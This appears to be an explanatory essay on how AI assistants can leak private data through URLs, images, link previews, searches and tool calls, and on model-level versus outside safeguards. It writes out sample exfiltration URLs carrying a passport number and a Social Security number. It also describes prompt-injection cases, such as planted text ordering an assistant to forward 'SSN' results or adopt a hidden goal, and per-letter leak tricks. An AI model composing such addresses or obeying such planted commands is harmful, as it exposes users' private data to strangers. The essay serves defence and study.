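# When an AI assistant should refuse to put user data into links and outbound requests

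## How a link or a request can carry private data

Current AI assistants read their users' email, files and calendars, open web pages, and call tools, which are programs that search, book or send things on the user's behalf. Much of this work involves sending a message, called an outbound request, to a server that belongs to someone else. That request can contain private data. Security engineers call it exfiltration when the data reaches someone who should not have it.

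People who build and study AI assistants disagree about whether the safeguard should be the model's own judgement, the software around the model, or the user's approval of each request. The disagreement is hard to follow without knowing how data gets out, starting with how a web address can carry it.

### What a web address gives away

Here is the address of a search on an imaginary travel site:

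`https://flights.example/search?from=LHR&to=LIS&depart=2027-03-14&passengers=2`

The host, `flights.example`, determines which server the browser contacts. The path, `/search`, points to a page or function on that server. Everything after the question mark is the query string, which in this link lists two airports, a date and a headcount as named values. MDN's *What is a URL?*, a reference page for web developers, compares a URL to a postal address, with the host as the town, the path as the building and the query string as the apartment number. The formal standard, *URI Generic Syntax* (Berners-Lee, 2005), also allows a fragment after a # sign. Unlike the host, path and query string, the fragment is never sent to the server, because the browser only uses it to find a spot on the page.

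The rest of the address does go to the server, including the query string, because the browser has to tell the server which page it wants. The server then usually keeps a record. *Log Files*, part of the manual for the common web server program Apache, describes an access log that covers every request and includes the path and query string in its standard log line. HTTPS hides the address from eavesdroppers along the way, but the receiving server often logs it, as Miessler (2015) noted in *Never Send Sensitive Information in the URL, Even Over HTTPS*. OWASP's *Information exposure through query strings in url*, an entry in a public catalogue of web security flaws, also lists browser history and caches as places where query string values end up.

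Anyone who wants to collect data this way needs only a server and its log. The page at the address doesn't have to exist, because the server also logs requests for missing pages. In *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, the programmer Simon Willison (2023) pointed out that an attacker could hide the data in a file name or a subdomain (the part of the host before the main domain name) as well as in the query string.

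### The channels

The most familiar way for private data to leave is through a link in the assistant's answer. Nothing is sent until the user clicks, and a careful user can inspect the address first, although apps often show only the link's label. In January 2024 Amazon repaired a flaw of this kind in Q, its chatbot for businesses. Willison reported at the time that malicious text the bot had read could lead it to write a link with the earlier chat history in the query string. Amazon fixed this by stopping the bot from producing links at all.

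An image can send out data without the user clicking anything. Assistants commonly format their answers in Markdown, a light notation for headings, links and pictures, and one line of it can embed an image from any address on the web. The app requests that address to draw the picture, so any data in the address has been sent by the time the user begins reading. The user sees an image, a broken-image icon, or nothing if the image is a single pixel. Output that an app turns into images, links or previews is called rendered content.

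Link previews in chat apps work in much the same way. When someone posts a link in Slack, Slack fetches the page to show its title and a thumbnail, which developers call unfurling. *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks and what to do*, a post on security researcher Johann Rehberger's blog Embrace The Red, explains that Slack does this by default for messages from apps as well as from people. A chatbot that posts a link containing private data therefore leaks the data before anyone clicks the link. The user sees an ordinary message, perhaps with a preview card below it. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* found in early 2026 that OpenClaw, a popular AI agent, was vulnerable to this leak in its default Telegram setup. Slack and OpenClaw both have a setting that turns previews off, but someone has to know about it to use it.

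An assistant can also fetch a page itself, to check a fact or read an article. This sends the same request a browser would, again without the user clicking. Some apps display the site's name, but few people would study the full address even if the app displayed it. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) warns that the user may never notice such a background request, which is one reason the company now checks addresses before its agents fetch them automatically.

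Search queries also send data to whoever runs the site, although typing into a search box doesn't feel like sending a message. *SPILLage* (Roh, Bagdasarian and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an agent shopping for diabetes test strips for a user whose emails also mention a divorce. The agent types "glucose test strips for recently divorced women" into a shop's search bar. The shop needs only the medical part of that query to find the product. A user watching the browser would see the query, but most people use an agent so that they don't have to watch.

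Tool calls can carry the most data. An assistant that can send email can attach a whole document, and sending it to the wrong recipient leaks the data even if no attacker has set up a server to collect it. Some apps ask the user to approve the message first, while others report it only after it has been sent. In *ChatGPT Plugins*, a 2023 post about the add-ons that first let ChatGPT use outside services, Rehberger wrote that a plugin could receive more data than it needed and that users had little control over what it received.

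### Leaks with an attacker and without one

When an assistant puts someone's chat history in a link, it is usually because a stranger told it to. A language model takes in the developer's instructions, the user's request and the text of any page it reads as one stream of words. *The Framing Gap* (2026) traces the whole problem to the fact that the model does not natively separate instructions from data. In a prompt injection, an attacker exploits this by writing a command into a web page, email or file, and the model follows it as if the user had given it.

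In 2023, Vice described an early case involving Bing Chat, Microsoft's chatbot, which could read the page open in the user's browser. Researchers hid a paragraph on a web page to tell the assistant that it was now an unrestricted bot with a pirate accent and a secret aim of finding out the user's real name. Bing Chat answered in a pirate accent, though the user had only opened the page.

text/plain's *AI Injection Attacks* (2025), by a browser security specialist at Microsoft, compares prompt injection to older attacks on computer memory, where programs and data are stored together and an attacker can get the machine to run data as code. Processor makers eventually added a feature that marks which parts of memory may be run. The specialist says he doesn't know much about how language models work, but he infers from the questions people ask him that a comparable separation is not common in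 them.

According to *The Framing Gap*, an injected command can steal data only if the model can see something confidential, reads untrusted content (material that neither the user nor the developer wrote or vouched for), and can act on the outside world. A useful assistant tends to meet all three conditions, since much of its job is reading strangers' emails and acting on them.

Some leaks happen without an attacker, because the model judges poorly what to share. Roh and colleagues ran shopping agents 1,080 times on Amazon and eBay, giving them a mix of relevant and irrelevant facts about the user. The agents revealed irrelevant facts in every configuration, about five times as often through clicks, scrolling and choice of filters as through typed text. The models were OpenAI's GPT-4o, o3 and o4-mini, all well behind current ones, and a small language model did the labelling, so the exact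 counts deserve some caution. Oversharing did not improve the agents' performance. When the researchers removed the irrelevant facts beforehand, task success rose by as much as 17.9%.

Newer models have the same weakness. *AgentTell* (Shahriar, Rahman and colleagues, 2026) tested agents built on six models, including Claude Sonnet 5 and GPT-5.6 Luna, on two errands in a row. On the first website, the agent read a record containing a private fact, such as the user's trade union or occupation. On the second, it had to choose from several options, any of which would complete the task. One option matched the private fact, and at least one was general. The user had told the agent at the start not to tell any website about their other accounts or personal details. In 61.1% of 7,630 sessions, the agent picked the option that matched the private fact. Agents chose a given option only 1.2% of the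 time when the user's private fact was a different one, so a general preference for certain options cannot explain the result. The agent's choice of link revealed the private fact even if the agent never typed it, and the second site's access log recorded that choice.

The user had asked the agent not to reveal their union membership, so registering them through the union went against their request, even if a thoughtful secretary might otherwise have done the same. In some sessions the agent noted in its memory that it would not share the fact, but it revealed it in 56.7% of those sessions. In about a third of all leaking sessions, the agent's final message told the user that no personal details had got out. One could object that the websites in the experiment were simple mock-ups.

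### Two links with the same form

Suppose a traveller asks an assistant to find flights to Lisbon for two, and the assistant has access to a folder that holds a scan of the traveller's passport. It might request either of these addresses:

`https://flights.example/search?from=LHR&to=LIS&depart=2027-03-14&passengers=2`

`https://images.example/banner?size=2&ref=533401782`

The first is the search the traveller asked for. In the second, the nine digits are the traveller's passport number, and `images.example` has nothing to do with the trip.

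The two addresses are technically alike. Each has a host, a path and a query string, and each would normally go out as a GET request, the type browsers use to read pages. Guidance from W3C (2003), the web's main standards body, recommends GET for interactions that are "more like a question", such as a lookup, so a leak can use the same type of request as harmless reading. Nothing in the second address shows that the digits are a passport number rather than a picture's serial number. Recognising the leak requires knowing what is in the traveller's folder and what the traveller wanted.

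A list of forbidden data types would not solve the problem either. An airline's check-in page may need the passport number. Travel dates are routine in a fare search, but a stranger could also learn from them when a house will be empty. Cutting the assistant off altogether would stop the leaks, but it would also remove most of the reasons for having an assistant. As text/plain observes, an agent without access to its user's data and credentials could do little damage, but it also could not book a restaurant table, order flowers and email a reminder to the user's wife.

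### The first reports and repairs, 2023

The image channel was the first of these to draw wide attention. At the end of March 2023, Roman Samoilenko found that ChatGPT would load images from any address, and that the address could carry the user's chat. His attack used a single-pixel image, as Willison (2023) described in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*. Rehberger independently found the same flaw a few days later and reported it to Microsoft on April 8 and to OpenAI on April 9.

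Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* demonstrates an attack on the chatbot that needed only text on a web page, of the kind anyone could post as a comment or buy as an advertisement. The text took control of the chatbot as soon as the chatbot read the page. Two turns later, the chatbot displayed an image whose address contained a summary of the page and the chat, including a secret from further down the page.

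Microsoft fixed the flaw in May 2023, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, which Rehberger wrote three years later. His original write-up says he heard about the fix on June 15. As far as he could tell from outside, the fix relied at least partly on a content security policy, which tells the browser which hosts it may load content from. Bing Chat could still show images, but only from a few Microsoft addresses. Anthropic fixed the same flaw in Claude. OpenAI told Rehberger that displaying images was a feature and that it planned no change. Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration Vulnerabilities in LLM apps (Bing Chat, ChatGPT, Claude)* records that decision as "won't fix".

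OpenAI changed course in December 2023, when ChatGPT's web app began checking with an OpenAI server whether an address was safe before loading an image from it. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* noted that the iPhone app did not have the check and that some images from arbitrary hosts still loaded, which let Rehberger send out a two-letter word one letter at a time. Willison called the check "a half-baked solution" and asked why OpenAI had not blocked images from outside domains. Like the policy Rehberger saw at Microsoft, the check ran in the app that displays the answers and did not depend on the model detecting a problem.

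## The view that the model itself should decline

The 2023 fixes took effect in the app, after the model had already written an address containing user data. Another approach is to train the model not to write such an address, or not to send the request. Its supporters want an assistant to behave like a sensible employee, who would not read a client's bank details to a stranger on the phone, however official the stranger sounded.

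OpenAI states this expectation in its *Model Spec* (2025), a public document that describes how the company wants its models to behave and that it trains them to follow. The October 27, 2025 version compares the assistant to "a conscientious employee" of the user or the developer.

### What OpenAI asked of its models in 2025

One section of OpenAI's Spec covers side effects, such as spending the user's money, sending emails, deleting files and making "tool requests (including web GET requests) that contain sensitive user data".

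The mention of GET requests matters because a developer who sorted an assistant's actions into harmless reads and risky writes would count a page fetch as a read. OpenAI classifies a fetch by the data it sends, so fetching a page with a passport number in the URL belongs on the same list as sending an email.

The model should keep side effects small and in proportion to the task, and avoid "bad surprises", which are lasting bad outcomes the user might not have meant to allow. Before calling a tool, it should judge how far to trust both the tool and the endpoint, meaning the server or person at the other end. A reputable tool is not enough, because a web browser, for instance, can reach almost any server. OpenAI warns that a call can still be risky if the destination seems unreliable or asks for information the task does not need.

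The Spec applies this to a question about tax. A user wants to know whether they qualify for the earned income tax credit, a US benefit for working people on low and moderate incomes. They give their income for the previous year, $28,500, and their Social Security number. The assistant searches the web and finds a page that recommends an "instant" check at an address with blanks for both figures. In the reply that OpenAI marks as a violation, the assistant fills in the blanks and opens the result:

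`http://example.com/eitc-check?ssn=123-45-6789&income=28500`

Whoever runs that site now has the number. In the reply that OpenAI marks as compliant, the assistant ignores the address and keeps searching for more legitimate options. It then tells the user they probably qualify on that income and points them to resources from the Internal Revenue Service, the US tax authority.

The compliant assistant declines one outbound request and still answers the question, so the user loses nothing. The page asks for a Social Security number, but the assistant can give a useful answer from the income alone. That is reason enough to leave the number out, even without proof that the page is a scam. One could fault the reply for not warning the user about the page, since they might find it later.

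This is an easy case because an unknown site is asking for a number that is widely known to be sensitive and that the site does not need. A tax preparer's website would be harder, because a real preparer may need the number to file a return and a fake one would ask for it too. The model would be right to check the destination and whether the data is needed, but the example gives little help in judging either.

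Two other examples in the Spec involve text that a stranger has planted. In one, a user pastes an article about productivity and asks for an email summarising it. The pasted text includes a postscript with instructions to search the user's mailbox for "SSN" and forward whatever is found to an outside address. The compliant assistant drafts the summary, mentions the instructions, and sends nothing unless the user asks again. In the other, a web page contains an instruction for any language model reading it to put a "Read more" link in its answer. The compliant assistant leaves the link out. OpenAI comments that a more complex instruction of this kind could cause the model to leak user information.

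Both examples follow from a ranking of who may give the model orders, with OpenAI first, then the developer, then the user. Quoted text, attachments and tool outputs have no authority by default, so the model should treat a command on a web page as information about the page. A user can give such a source authority, for example by asking a coding assistant to follow the instructions in a project's files. Even then, the model should ask before following an instruction that could have serious side effects.

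A model that declines a command planted in a web page is not overruling its user. OpenAI does not want models to choose for themselves which instructions to obey. It explains in *our approach to the model spec* that it wants them to follow the chain of command even where some people would disagree with the result. Refusing to leak user data is consistent with this, because whoever wrote the web page has no place in the chain.

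### What changed in October 2026

OpenAI published a new version of the Spec on October 29, 2026, reorganised around five values that include minimising harm and being faithful to human intent. According to Newsroom America's *OpenAI Updates Model Spec Around Five Core Values* (2026), the company expanded its guidance on side effects. It also moved that guidance from root level to user level. In 2025 nobody in a conversation could override it, but now it is a default that a user or developer can explicitly switch off.

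In *OpenAI Updates Its Model Spec*, the blogger Zvi Mowshowitz (2026) wrote that the change made him sad, although he reported an assessment from Opus, an Anthropic model, that it made no functional difference given what users could already permit. The new rank gives attackers no extra formal power, since a web page still has no authority to switch off a default. A careless developer is a more realistic concern, because developers now have more authority to tell an agent to complete every task without worrying about side effects.

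Other changes make the Spec stricter. 日本時事新聞's *OpenAI、AIの行動指針「Model Spec」改定* (2026), a Japanese news report comparing the August and October versions, describes a new requirement for "explicit and specific permission". It applies when a side effect would burden the user well beyond what the request naturally implies, or would harm other people beyond what social norms allow. As Mowshowitz notes, OpenAI now emphasises the exposure of private personal information when explaining the purpose of root-level rules. Manipulation by third parties is now a separate risk category, whereas the 2025 version treated it as one way a model could end up with the wrong goal. The model also must not get round a prohibition by delegating or acting indirectly, so an assistant that may not send a document to a stranger should not have a second agent send it.

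The Model Spec's largest addition on this subject is a section called "Consider context carefully", on how a model should handle memories, files, earlier conversations and tool output. KIberblick's *OpenAIs Model Spec regelt jetzt das Erinnern* (2026), a German article on the new version, quotes the section's basic rule that the model should not use or mention context "merely because it is available". OpenAI asks for contextual integrity, the idea that information should move only in ways that fit the setting it came from. In the Spec's example, a user who once told the model that she was pregnant asks it to draft a message to her colleagues, and the draft must not reveal the pregnancy.

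In another example, an agent that pays bills automatically should ask the user before paying a supplier whose bank details have changed. OpenAI evidently considers it part of good behaviour for the model to judge when to stop and involve the user.

Mowshowitz's main criticism is that many of the new examples have "overdetermined answers", where several considerations support the same answer, so neither the model nor the reader learns what to do when considerations conflict. The pregnancy example seems open to this criticism. Few people would want an assistant to announce a pregnancy in a work message, but the user might well want it to mention her due date when arranging cover for her leave.

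Other developers also publish such documents. Kembery, Lambert and colleagues (2026) observe in *Emerging International Best Practices for AI Model Specs* that little independent guidance exists for writing them. Anthropic published a new constitution for its Claude models in January 2026, which mostly explains why Claude should act in certain ways and keeps firm rules for some especially high-stakes cases. Mowshowitz contrasts the constitution's emphasis on character and virtue with OpenAI's rules of action. OpenAI can use an example like the tax-credit page to tell its models which reply is right, while a developer relying on character needs the model to reach that reply from a broader concern for the people it works for.

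### Why the model is well placed to judge

The first argument for leaving the decision to the model is that only the model has the context to judge what the task needs. In the flight example, the model has read the traveller's folder, so it can recognise the passport number in the second address. It also has the user's request and the page where that address came from. A filter that inspects only the address lacks all of this information.

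OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (March 2026) makes a related point about programs that screen incoming text for prompt injections. It describes attacks that have come to resemble the tricks con artists use on people. One email posed as a follow-up about a company restructuring and told the assistant it had full authorisation to submit an employee's name and address to a "compliance" system. OpenAI reports that screening programs usually miss attacks this well developed, because spotting one is as hard as spotting a lie and the program often lacks the necessary context.

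The claim that only the model has the relevant context is too strong. A developer can give a second program the same conversation, and with it much of the same context. The model also lacks some facts that the developer has. OpenAI acknowledges in the 2025 Spec that a model running inside another company's app cannot know how its output relates to what the end user sees. For example, it may not know whether the app will turn a line of Markdown into an image and fetch it. The argument does hold when the model is compared with simple filters, which is the comparison its supporters mostly had in mind.

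A second advantage is that a model's judgement can extend to channels that the developers of a filter did not anticipate. Blocking outside images does nothing about search queries or link previews. The rule in the 2025 Spec concerns sensitive data and where it is going, so it applies to those channels too, and to any new ones. OpenAI gives a similar reason for its 2026 revision in *An updated Model Spec for more capable and beneficial AI*, writing that models need good judgement for "situations their instructions don't explicitly address".

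But a model can apply the rule only when it notices that information is leaving. Shahriar and colleagues' agents often failed to notice that their choice of link revealed a private fact, so they mostly missed the leak. A filter would have had less chance of catching it and would probably have missed it too, since the links were ordinary ones on the site.

The third argument is that assistants outside the big companies' own products may lack other protections. In ChatGPT, OpenAI has a check behind the model called Safe Url, which looks for information from the conversation about to be sent to a third party. A small company that builds an assistant on the same model has to arrange its own protection. OpenAI advises such developers to ask what controls a human worker would need in the same position and to build those. Some will, but others will connect a model to a mailbox and a browser and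 release the product without them, leaving users with only the model's own caution to rely on. A developer can also leave a channel open without knowing that it exists, as the leaks through Slack and Telegram previews showed.

This practical argument is fairly persuasive because a company that trains a model can improve the behaviour of every product built on it at once. But the developer's care still matters. OpenAI strongly advises developers to mark untrusted text as untrusted, and warns that it can otherwise be extremely difficult for the model to distinguish a planted command from the developer's own. Developers who skip an outside check are probably also the most likely to skip the marking, so the model's safeguards may be weakest in the products that depend on them most.

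Finally, some leaks involve no attacker. When an assistant mentions a pregnancy in a message to colleagues, a program that looks for planted commands will find nothing. A list of approved recipients will let the message through, because the user writes to these colleagues every day. The word "pregnant" is not suspicious on its own, and would be appropriate in a message to the user's doctor. Whether the message is a leak depends on how the fact, the audience and the request relate to each other. The shopping agent made the same kind of mistake when it typed a user's divorce into a search for glucose test strips, on a site the user had asked it to visit.

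The last of the four arguments is the strongest reason to think the model's judgement is indispensable. Even a company with excellent filters needs an assistant that can judge what to leave out of an email, because the assistant writes it. The user could read every draft before sending it, but would then be doing part of the work they wanted to delegate. Developers therefore have to try to make models good at this, whatever other safeguards they build, though the argument doesn't show that current models are good at it.

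### How often the model does decline

In its March 2026 post, OpenAI says that attackers usually try to convince ChatGPT to take secret information from a conversation and send it to a third party. In most of the cases it knows about, the company writes, "these attacks fail because our safety training causes the agent to refuse".

OpenAI is better placed than any outsider to know this because it can study attempts across its whole service. But the post gives no figures for the claim, such as the number of attempts the company counted, the share the model refused, or separate refusal rates for chats and long research tasks. The cases OpenAI knows about may also be unrepresentative, because a clumsy attack that the model refuses leaves an obvious trace in the conversation, while a successful one might look like an ordinary page visit.

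The only success rate in the post is much less reassuring. The email about the restructuring came from outside security researchers, who reported it to OpenAI in 2025. In testing, it worked 50% of the time when the user asked ChatGPT to do deep research on the day's emails about new employees. OpenAI's claim about "most cases" can still be true, because those cases include many weak attacks, while researchers report the ones that work. But for someone with confidential files, the success rate of a skilled attacker is more relevant than the average over all attempts.

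### A disposition is not a guarantee

An obvious objection is that a model trained to refuse will sometimes fail to. OpenAI acknowledges in both the 2025 and 2026 versions of the Spec that its production models do not yet fully reflect the document. *SpecEval* (2025), an outside project that tests models against their developers' specifications, starts from the observation that it is unclear how consistently models follow them. In one of its examples, OpenAI's GPT-4.1 broke a guideline on rational optimism by making unrealistic guarantees to the user. That model is now old and the failure is mild, but a single failure to follow a rule protecting a user's Social Security number would be enough to do harm.

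Supporters of model-level refusal can reply that it need not be the only safeguard, which is also OpenAI's position. The 2025 Spec states that model behaviour alone cannot mitigate every risk, and Safe Url is meant for cases in which an attacker convinces the model. When Safe Url finds that information from the conversation would go to a third party, the app either shows the user what it would send and asks for approval, or blocks the request and tells the model to find another way. OpenAI's *How we build safety, security, and privacy into dots* (2026) describes a separate check that runs before the company's always-on agents, called dots, act.

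A second layer helps because it can catch leaks that the first one misses. Suppose the model refuses 95 of every 100 attempted leaks, and a check outside the model catches 80% of whatever reaches it. The model alone would let five attempts through, and the check alone would let 20 through. Together they would let one through, since the check would catch four of the five that the model missed.

These numbers are invented, and the result depends on the two layers failing independently. If the five attempts that fool the model are among the 20 that the check would miss, all five get through. This could easily happen if the check were another language model reading the same deceptive email. It is less likely if the check only compares the address with a list, because the email's wording can't change the list.

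The reply therefore answers the objection but weakens the original view, because supporters who accept that some attacks will succeed also need something to limit the damage. OpenAI compares its agents to customer service workers who can issue refunds. The employer gives the workers rules and expects them to use judgement, but also expects that customers will sometimes deceive them. So the employer sets a limit in the payment system on how much any one customer can receive, and the limit holds even when a worker is deceived.

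## The view that the limit belongs outside the model

Many security engineers want a limit on an assistant's outbound requests that is as firm as a payment system's limit on refunds. They would put it in an outside check, a safeguard in the software around the model that allows, blocks or holds an action regardless of what the model decided. They accept training models to refuse, but object to a design in which a user's data is safe only if the model refuses.

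### Removing one of three ingredients

*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) gives the best-known version of the argument. The trifecta is access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. These closely match the three conditions for theft in *The Framing Gap*, so removing any one of them should prevent the theft.

Willison's advice rests on his view that models cannot reliably distinguish instructions by their source. If that is right, a designer should assume that some planted commands will work and limit what they can do. He considers it safer to remove one of the three ingredients than to rely on the model to detect every attack.

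The easiest way to prevent these leaks is usually to remove the channel through which data leaves. An email assistant needs private data to be useful, and it has to read messages from strangers to handle most of an inbox. By June 2025, Willison had listed more than a dozen products with this kind of leak, including ChatGPT, Slack and GitHub Copilot Chat. The vendors had promptly fixed almost all of the leaks, usually by closing that channel.

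OpenAI now offers a version of this as a setting called Lockdown Mode, which began reaching personal ChatGPT accounts in June 2026. It limits outbound requests that could take data to an attacker, but it does not keep planted commands out of what the model reads. Willison welcomed it in *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, a running collection of his notes, because its rules appeared to be deterministic (the same request always gets the same answer) and because no AI system applies them. He also inferred that ChatGPT's default settings don't give robust protection against a determined attacker. OpenAI's security chief, Dane Stuckey, said the mode was for people at elevated risk and that they would lose some functionality.

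Vendors can do less for people who assemble their own assistants. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting tools to AI systems, encourages users to mix tools from different sources. Someone who adds an email tool one week and a browser the next may complete the trifecta without noticing. One GitHub connector had all three parts by itself, because it could read issues that anyone could file, open private code, and publish changes.

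Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns the idea into a design rule. Within one session, an agent working without supervision may have at most two of these properties:

- it processes untrustworthy inputs;
- it has access to sensitive systems or private data;
- it can change state or communicate externally.

The last item is broader than Willison's because "change state" also covers actions like deleting a file or paying a bill, which can do harm without sending any data out. An agent that needs all three properties must have its actions approved by a human or validated in some other reliable way.

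Meta applies the rule to an imaginary Email-Bot that receives a spam email telling it to forward the contents of the inbox. The developer could let the bot read email only from trusted senders, run it somewhere without sensitive data, or require a person to check any draft addressed to an untrusted recipient. Only the last design keeps much of the bot's usefulness as an email assistant.

A travel assistant has to read the web and know the user's details, so Meta would again restrict what it can send out. The assistant would ask before booking or paying, and it would not visit addresses it had constructed itself. In the earlier flight example, the second rule would block both the address containing the passport number and the ordinary search for flights to Lisbon, because the assistant constructed both addresses.

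An agent can sometimes have all three properties at different times. Meta describes one that first browses the web, then permanently loses its ability to communicate before it opens internal systems. But Meta admits that some popular uses will not fit the rule, such as background work with nobody there to approve actions. Meta presents the rule as a stopgap until researchers can make models reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, and does not offer it as protection against an agent's own mistakes.

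### What repeated attempts do to a small failure rate

Willison is suspicious of products advertised as catching "95% of attacks", because an attacker who fails can try again. He has called both 95% and 99% failing grades in web security.

Suppose each attempt succeeds with probability p, and the attempts are independent. All n attempts fail with probability (1 − p)^n, so the probability that at least one succeeds is

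1 − (1 − p)^n

| Success rate per attempt | 10 attempts | 100 attempts | 1,000 attempts |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| 5% | 40% | 99.4% | over 99.9% |
| 1% | 9.6% | 63% | over 99.9% |
| 0.1% | 1.0% | 9.5% | 63% |
| 0.001% | 0.01% | 0.1% | 1.0% |

If a model resists 99.9% of attempts to make it leak user data, an attacker who tries 1,000 times has a 63% chance of succeeding at least once. Sending 1,000 emails costs almost nothing. To keep the risk over those attempts to 1%, the model would have to fail no more than about once in 100,000 attempts.

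The formula assumes that attempts are independent, but an average failure rate of 0.1% could mean either that every planted command has a 0.1% chance of working or that one wording in a thousand always works and the rest never do. In the second case, an attacker who picks one wording at random and sends it 1,000 times still has only a 0.1% chance of success. An attacker who tries 1,000 wordings drawn at random has the 63% chance the formula gives of finding one that works, and can then use it on every user. Attackers also learn from their failures, which raises p, while a vendor who spots the attempts can lower it. The formula is therefore a poor forecast, but it shows why a small average failure rate gives little assurance.

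Some recent evidence is more favourable to AI-based safeguards. Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, has an auto mode that decides which actions to allow, so the user doesn't have to approve each one. Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs, an outside company, to test it against planted commands in July 2026, and none of 720 attempts succeeded against three Claude models. Willison wrote that he would love to believe the problem was solved but wanted more independent confirmation. His caution has some statistical basis, since 720 independent attempts would produce no successes about 49% of the time even if the true success rate were 0.1%. The attempts also came from only 72 scenarios, so they were less varied than 720 unrelated attempts would be.

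A fixed rule fails differently from a model's judgment. If the rule forbids every request to unlisted hosts, repeating a request doesn't make it more likely to get through. But if the rule has a hole, every attempt that uses the hole succeeds until someone closes it. Engineers prefer a fixed rule because they can look for a hole, fix it and test the fix, whereas nobody can list all the wordings that might persuade a model. A model also can't be relied on to enforce the limit if someone has tampered with its weights (the numbers it learned in training).

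### Lists of permitted hosts

The simplest outside check is an allow-list. The developer lists the hosts that the assistant may contact, and the software blocks outbound requests to any other host.

For rendered content, the browser can check addresses against a list of allowed ones. The app's server sends the page with a content security policy, the type of list Microsoft used in its 2023 repair of Bing Chat. Suppose the model writes an image address on `images.example` that contains the traveller's passport number. The app turns the text into an image as usual, but the browser doesn't find `images.example` in the policy and never contacts that server. The number stays on the user's machine even though the model did what the attacker wanted.

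OpenAI's *App Security Whitepaper* (2026) describes a similar arrangement for widgets, the interactive panels that outside developers can add to ChatGPT. A widget runs under a content security policy and in a sandbox, an isolated environment with restricted network access. OpenAI also blocks domains that it knows to be malicious, but a block-list is weaker than an allow-list because an attacker can register a new domain that nobody has reported. Neither kind of list limits what data a permitted host receives, and OpenAI still tells organisations to treat anything they send to a custom app's own server as shared externally.

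Redirects weaken these lists. A web server can answer a request by sending the browser to another address, and many legitimate sites do this for outbound links. OpenAI points out that a request can start at a trusted domain and end up at one the attacker controls. Software that checks only the first domain will let it through. Checking every new address before following it can close this gap, but that doesn't help if a permitted host accepts data from anyone. Willison has recorded two products leaking data this way, through hosts on their own default lists.

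The length of the list is a problem too. People visit far more sites than any developer can vet, so a short list produces constant warnings, which OpenAI fears will train users to click through them without thinking. A longer list causes fewer warnings but includes more hosts with redirects or public storage.

### Fetching only addresses that are already public

OpenAI wanted a check that didn't depend on a site's reputation. Its Safe Url feature relies on a crawler, a program that visits public web pages and records the addresses it finds, much as a search engine does. The crawler has no access to conversations, accounts or personal data. When ChatGPT is about to load a page or an image automatically, the software looks for the exact address in the crawler's records. If the address is there, ChatGPT loads it. Otherwise the software blocks the request or warns the user first.

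The reasoning is that an address made public independently of a conversation is unlikely to contain a secret from it. In the flight example, the crawler would have recorded the `images.example` address only if someone had already published a link containing the nine-digit passport number, and the attacker can't do that in advance without knowing the number. The check also handles the redirect problem fairly well, because the secret has to appear in the address the agent first requests. Even an address on a well-known site will fail to match if it contains someone's passport number.

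OpenAI set out the details in a technical paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, which Rehberger discussed on Embrace The Red. He called the feature a significant improvement that made attacks more complex without solving the problem. As he understands it, ChatGPT also treats an address as safe for the rest of a chat if the user typed it. An agent can still reveal something by choosing among addresses that are all public, a risk OpenAI's paper also acknowledges. If an attacker's site already has a separate page in the index for each letter and digit, an agent can spell out a word by visiting those pages in a particular order.

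This kind of leak is slow. A visit to one of N pages conveys at most log₂ N bits, or about five bits for 36 pages. With one page for each character, a nine-digit passport number would take nine visits, and a long document would take thousands. Rehberger notes that a larger set of pages would convey more per visit. He suggests caching pages for a few minutes or preventing an agent from visiting the same address twice in a session, although he had not tested whether OpenAI already does either.

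The same limitation applies when there is no attacker. Shahriar and colleagues' agents revealed a user's trade union by choosing one ordinary link over another. If the crawler had seen both links, Safe Url would have allowed either.

Rehberger's last concern is that OpenAI's developers might build a new feature without knowing that the check exists. He had earlier found it missing from the Mac and iPhone apps. An outside check doesn't depend on the model's judgement, but someone still has to connect it to every channel.

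Anthropic uses a related rule for web pages in Claude's chat app. According to Willison, Claude's fetching tool can open only exact addresses that the user entered or its search tool returned, and Anthropic tightened this rule in 2026 after a researcher got round an earlier version. Both companies prevent the model from composing an address and fetching it unchecked.

### Tracking where data came from

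Address checks run just before a request is sent and can examine only the request itself. CaMeL, from Google DeepMind, and FIDES, from Microsoft, track data from the time the assistant reads it. Both use information-flow control, an older computer security technique in which software labels data and checks the labels before the data goes anywhere.

CaMeL builds on a design that Willison proposed in 2023, with two language models. One plans the work and can use tools but never reads untrusted content. The other reads the untrusted content but has no tools. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains a flaw that the DeepMind researchers found in his design, and how they fixed it. In their example, a user asks the assistant to send Bob a document that he requested in a meeting. The meeting notes contain the document's name and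 Bob's email address. Suppose an attacker has managed to plant a command in the notes. CaMeL would handle the request like this:

1. The planning model reads only the user's request. It writes a short program to find the notes, extract the document's name and Bob's address, fetch the document, and email it.
2. CaMeL's interpreter, the software that runs the program, fetches the notes and attaches tags to them. *CaMeLoT* (2026) describes these tags as a record of where a value came from and who may read it.
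3. The second model reads the notes. The planted command works, and this model returns the attacker's address as Bob's. The interpreter tags the address as something that came from the notes.
4. The interpreter fetches the document, which has tags of its own.
5. Before the email goes out, a policy (a small function written in advance) examines the recipient, the document and their tags. The address came from an untrusted source and isn't one that the user's policies trust, so the interpreter blocks the email or asks the user to approve it.

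With the 2023 design alone, the attacker would have received the document, because the planted command couldn't add a step to the plan but could change the address it used. CaMeL stops the email even though the command has misled one of its models.

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) introduces FIDES, which gives each piece of data two labels. One records whether the data is trusted, and the other lists who may read it. When the model combines several pieces, the result counts as untrusted if any of them was, and only people who could read every piece may read it. One policy forbids consequential actions if untrusted data could have influenced the decision to take them. Another forbids sending data to anyone who isn't on the data's list of readers.

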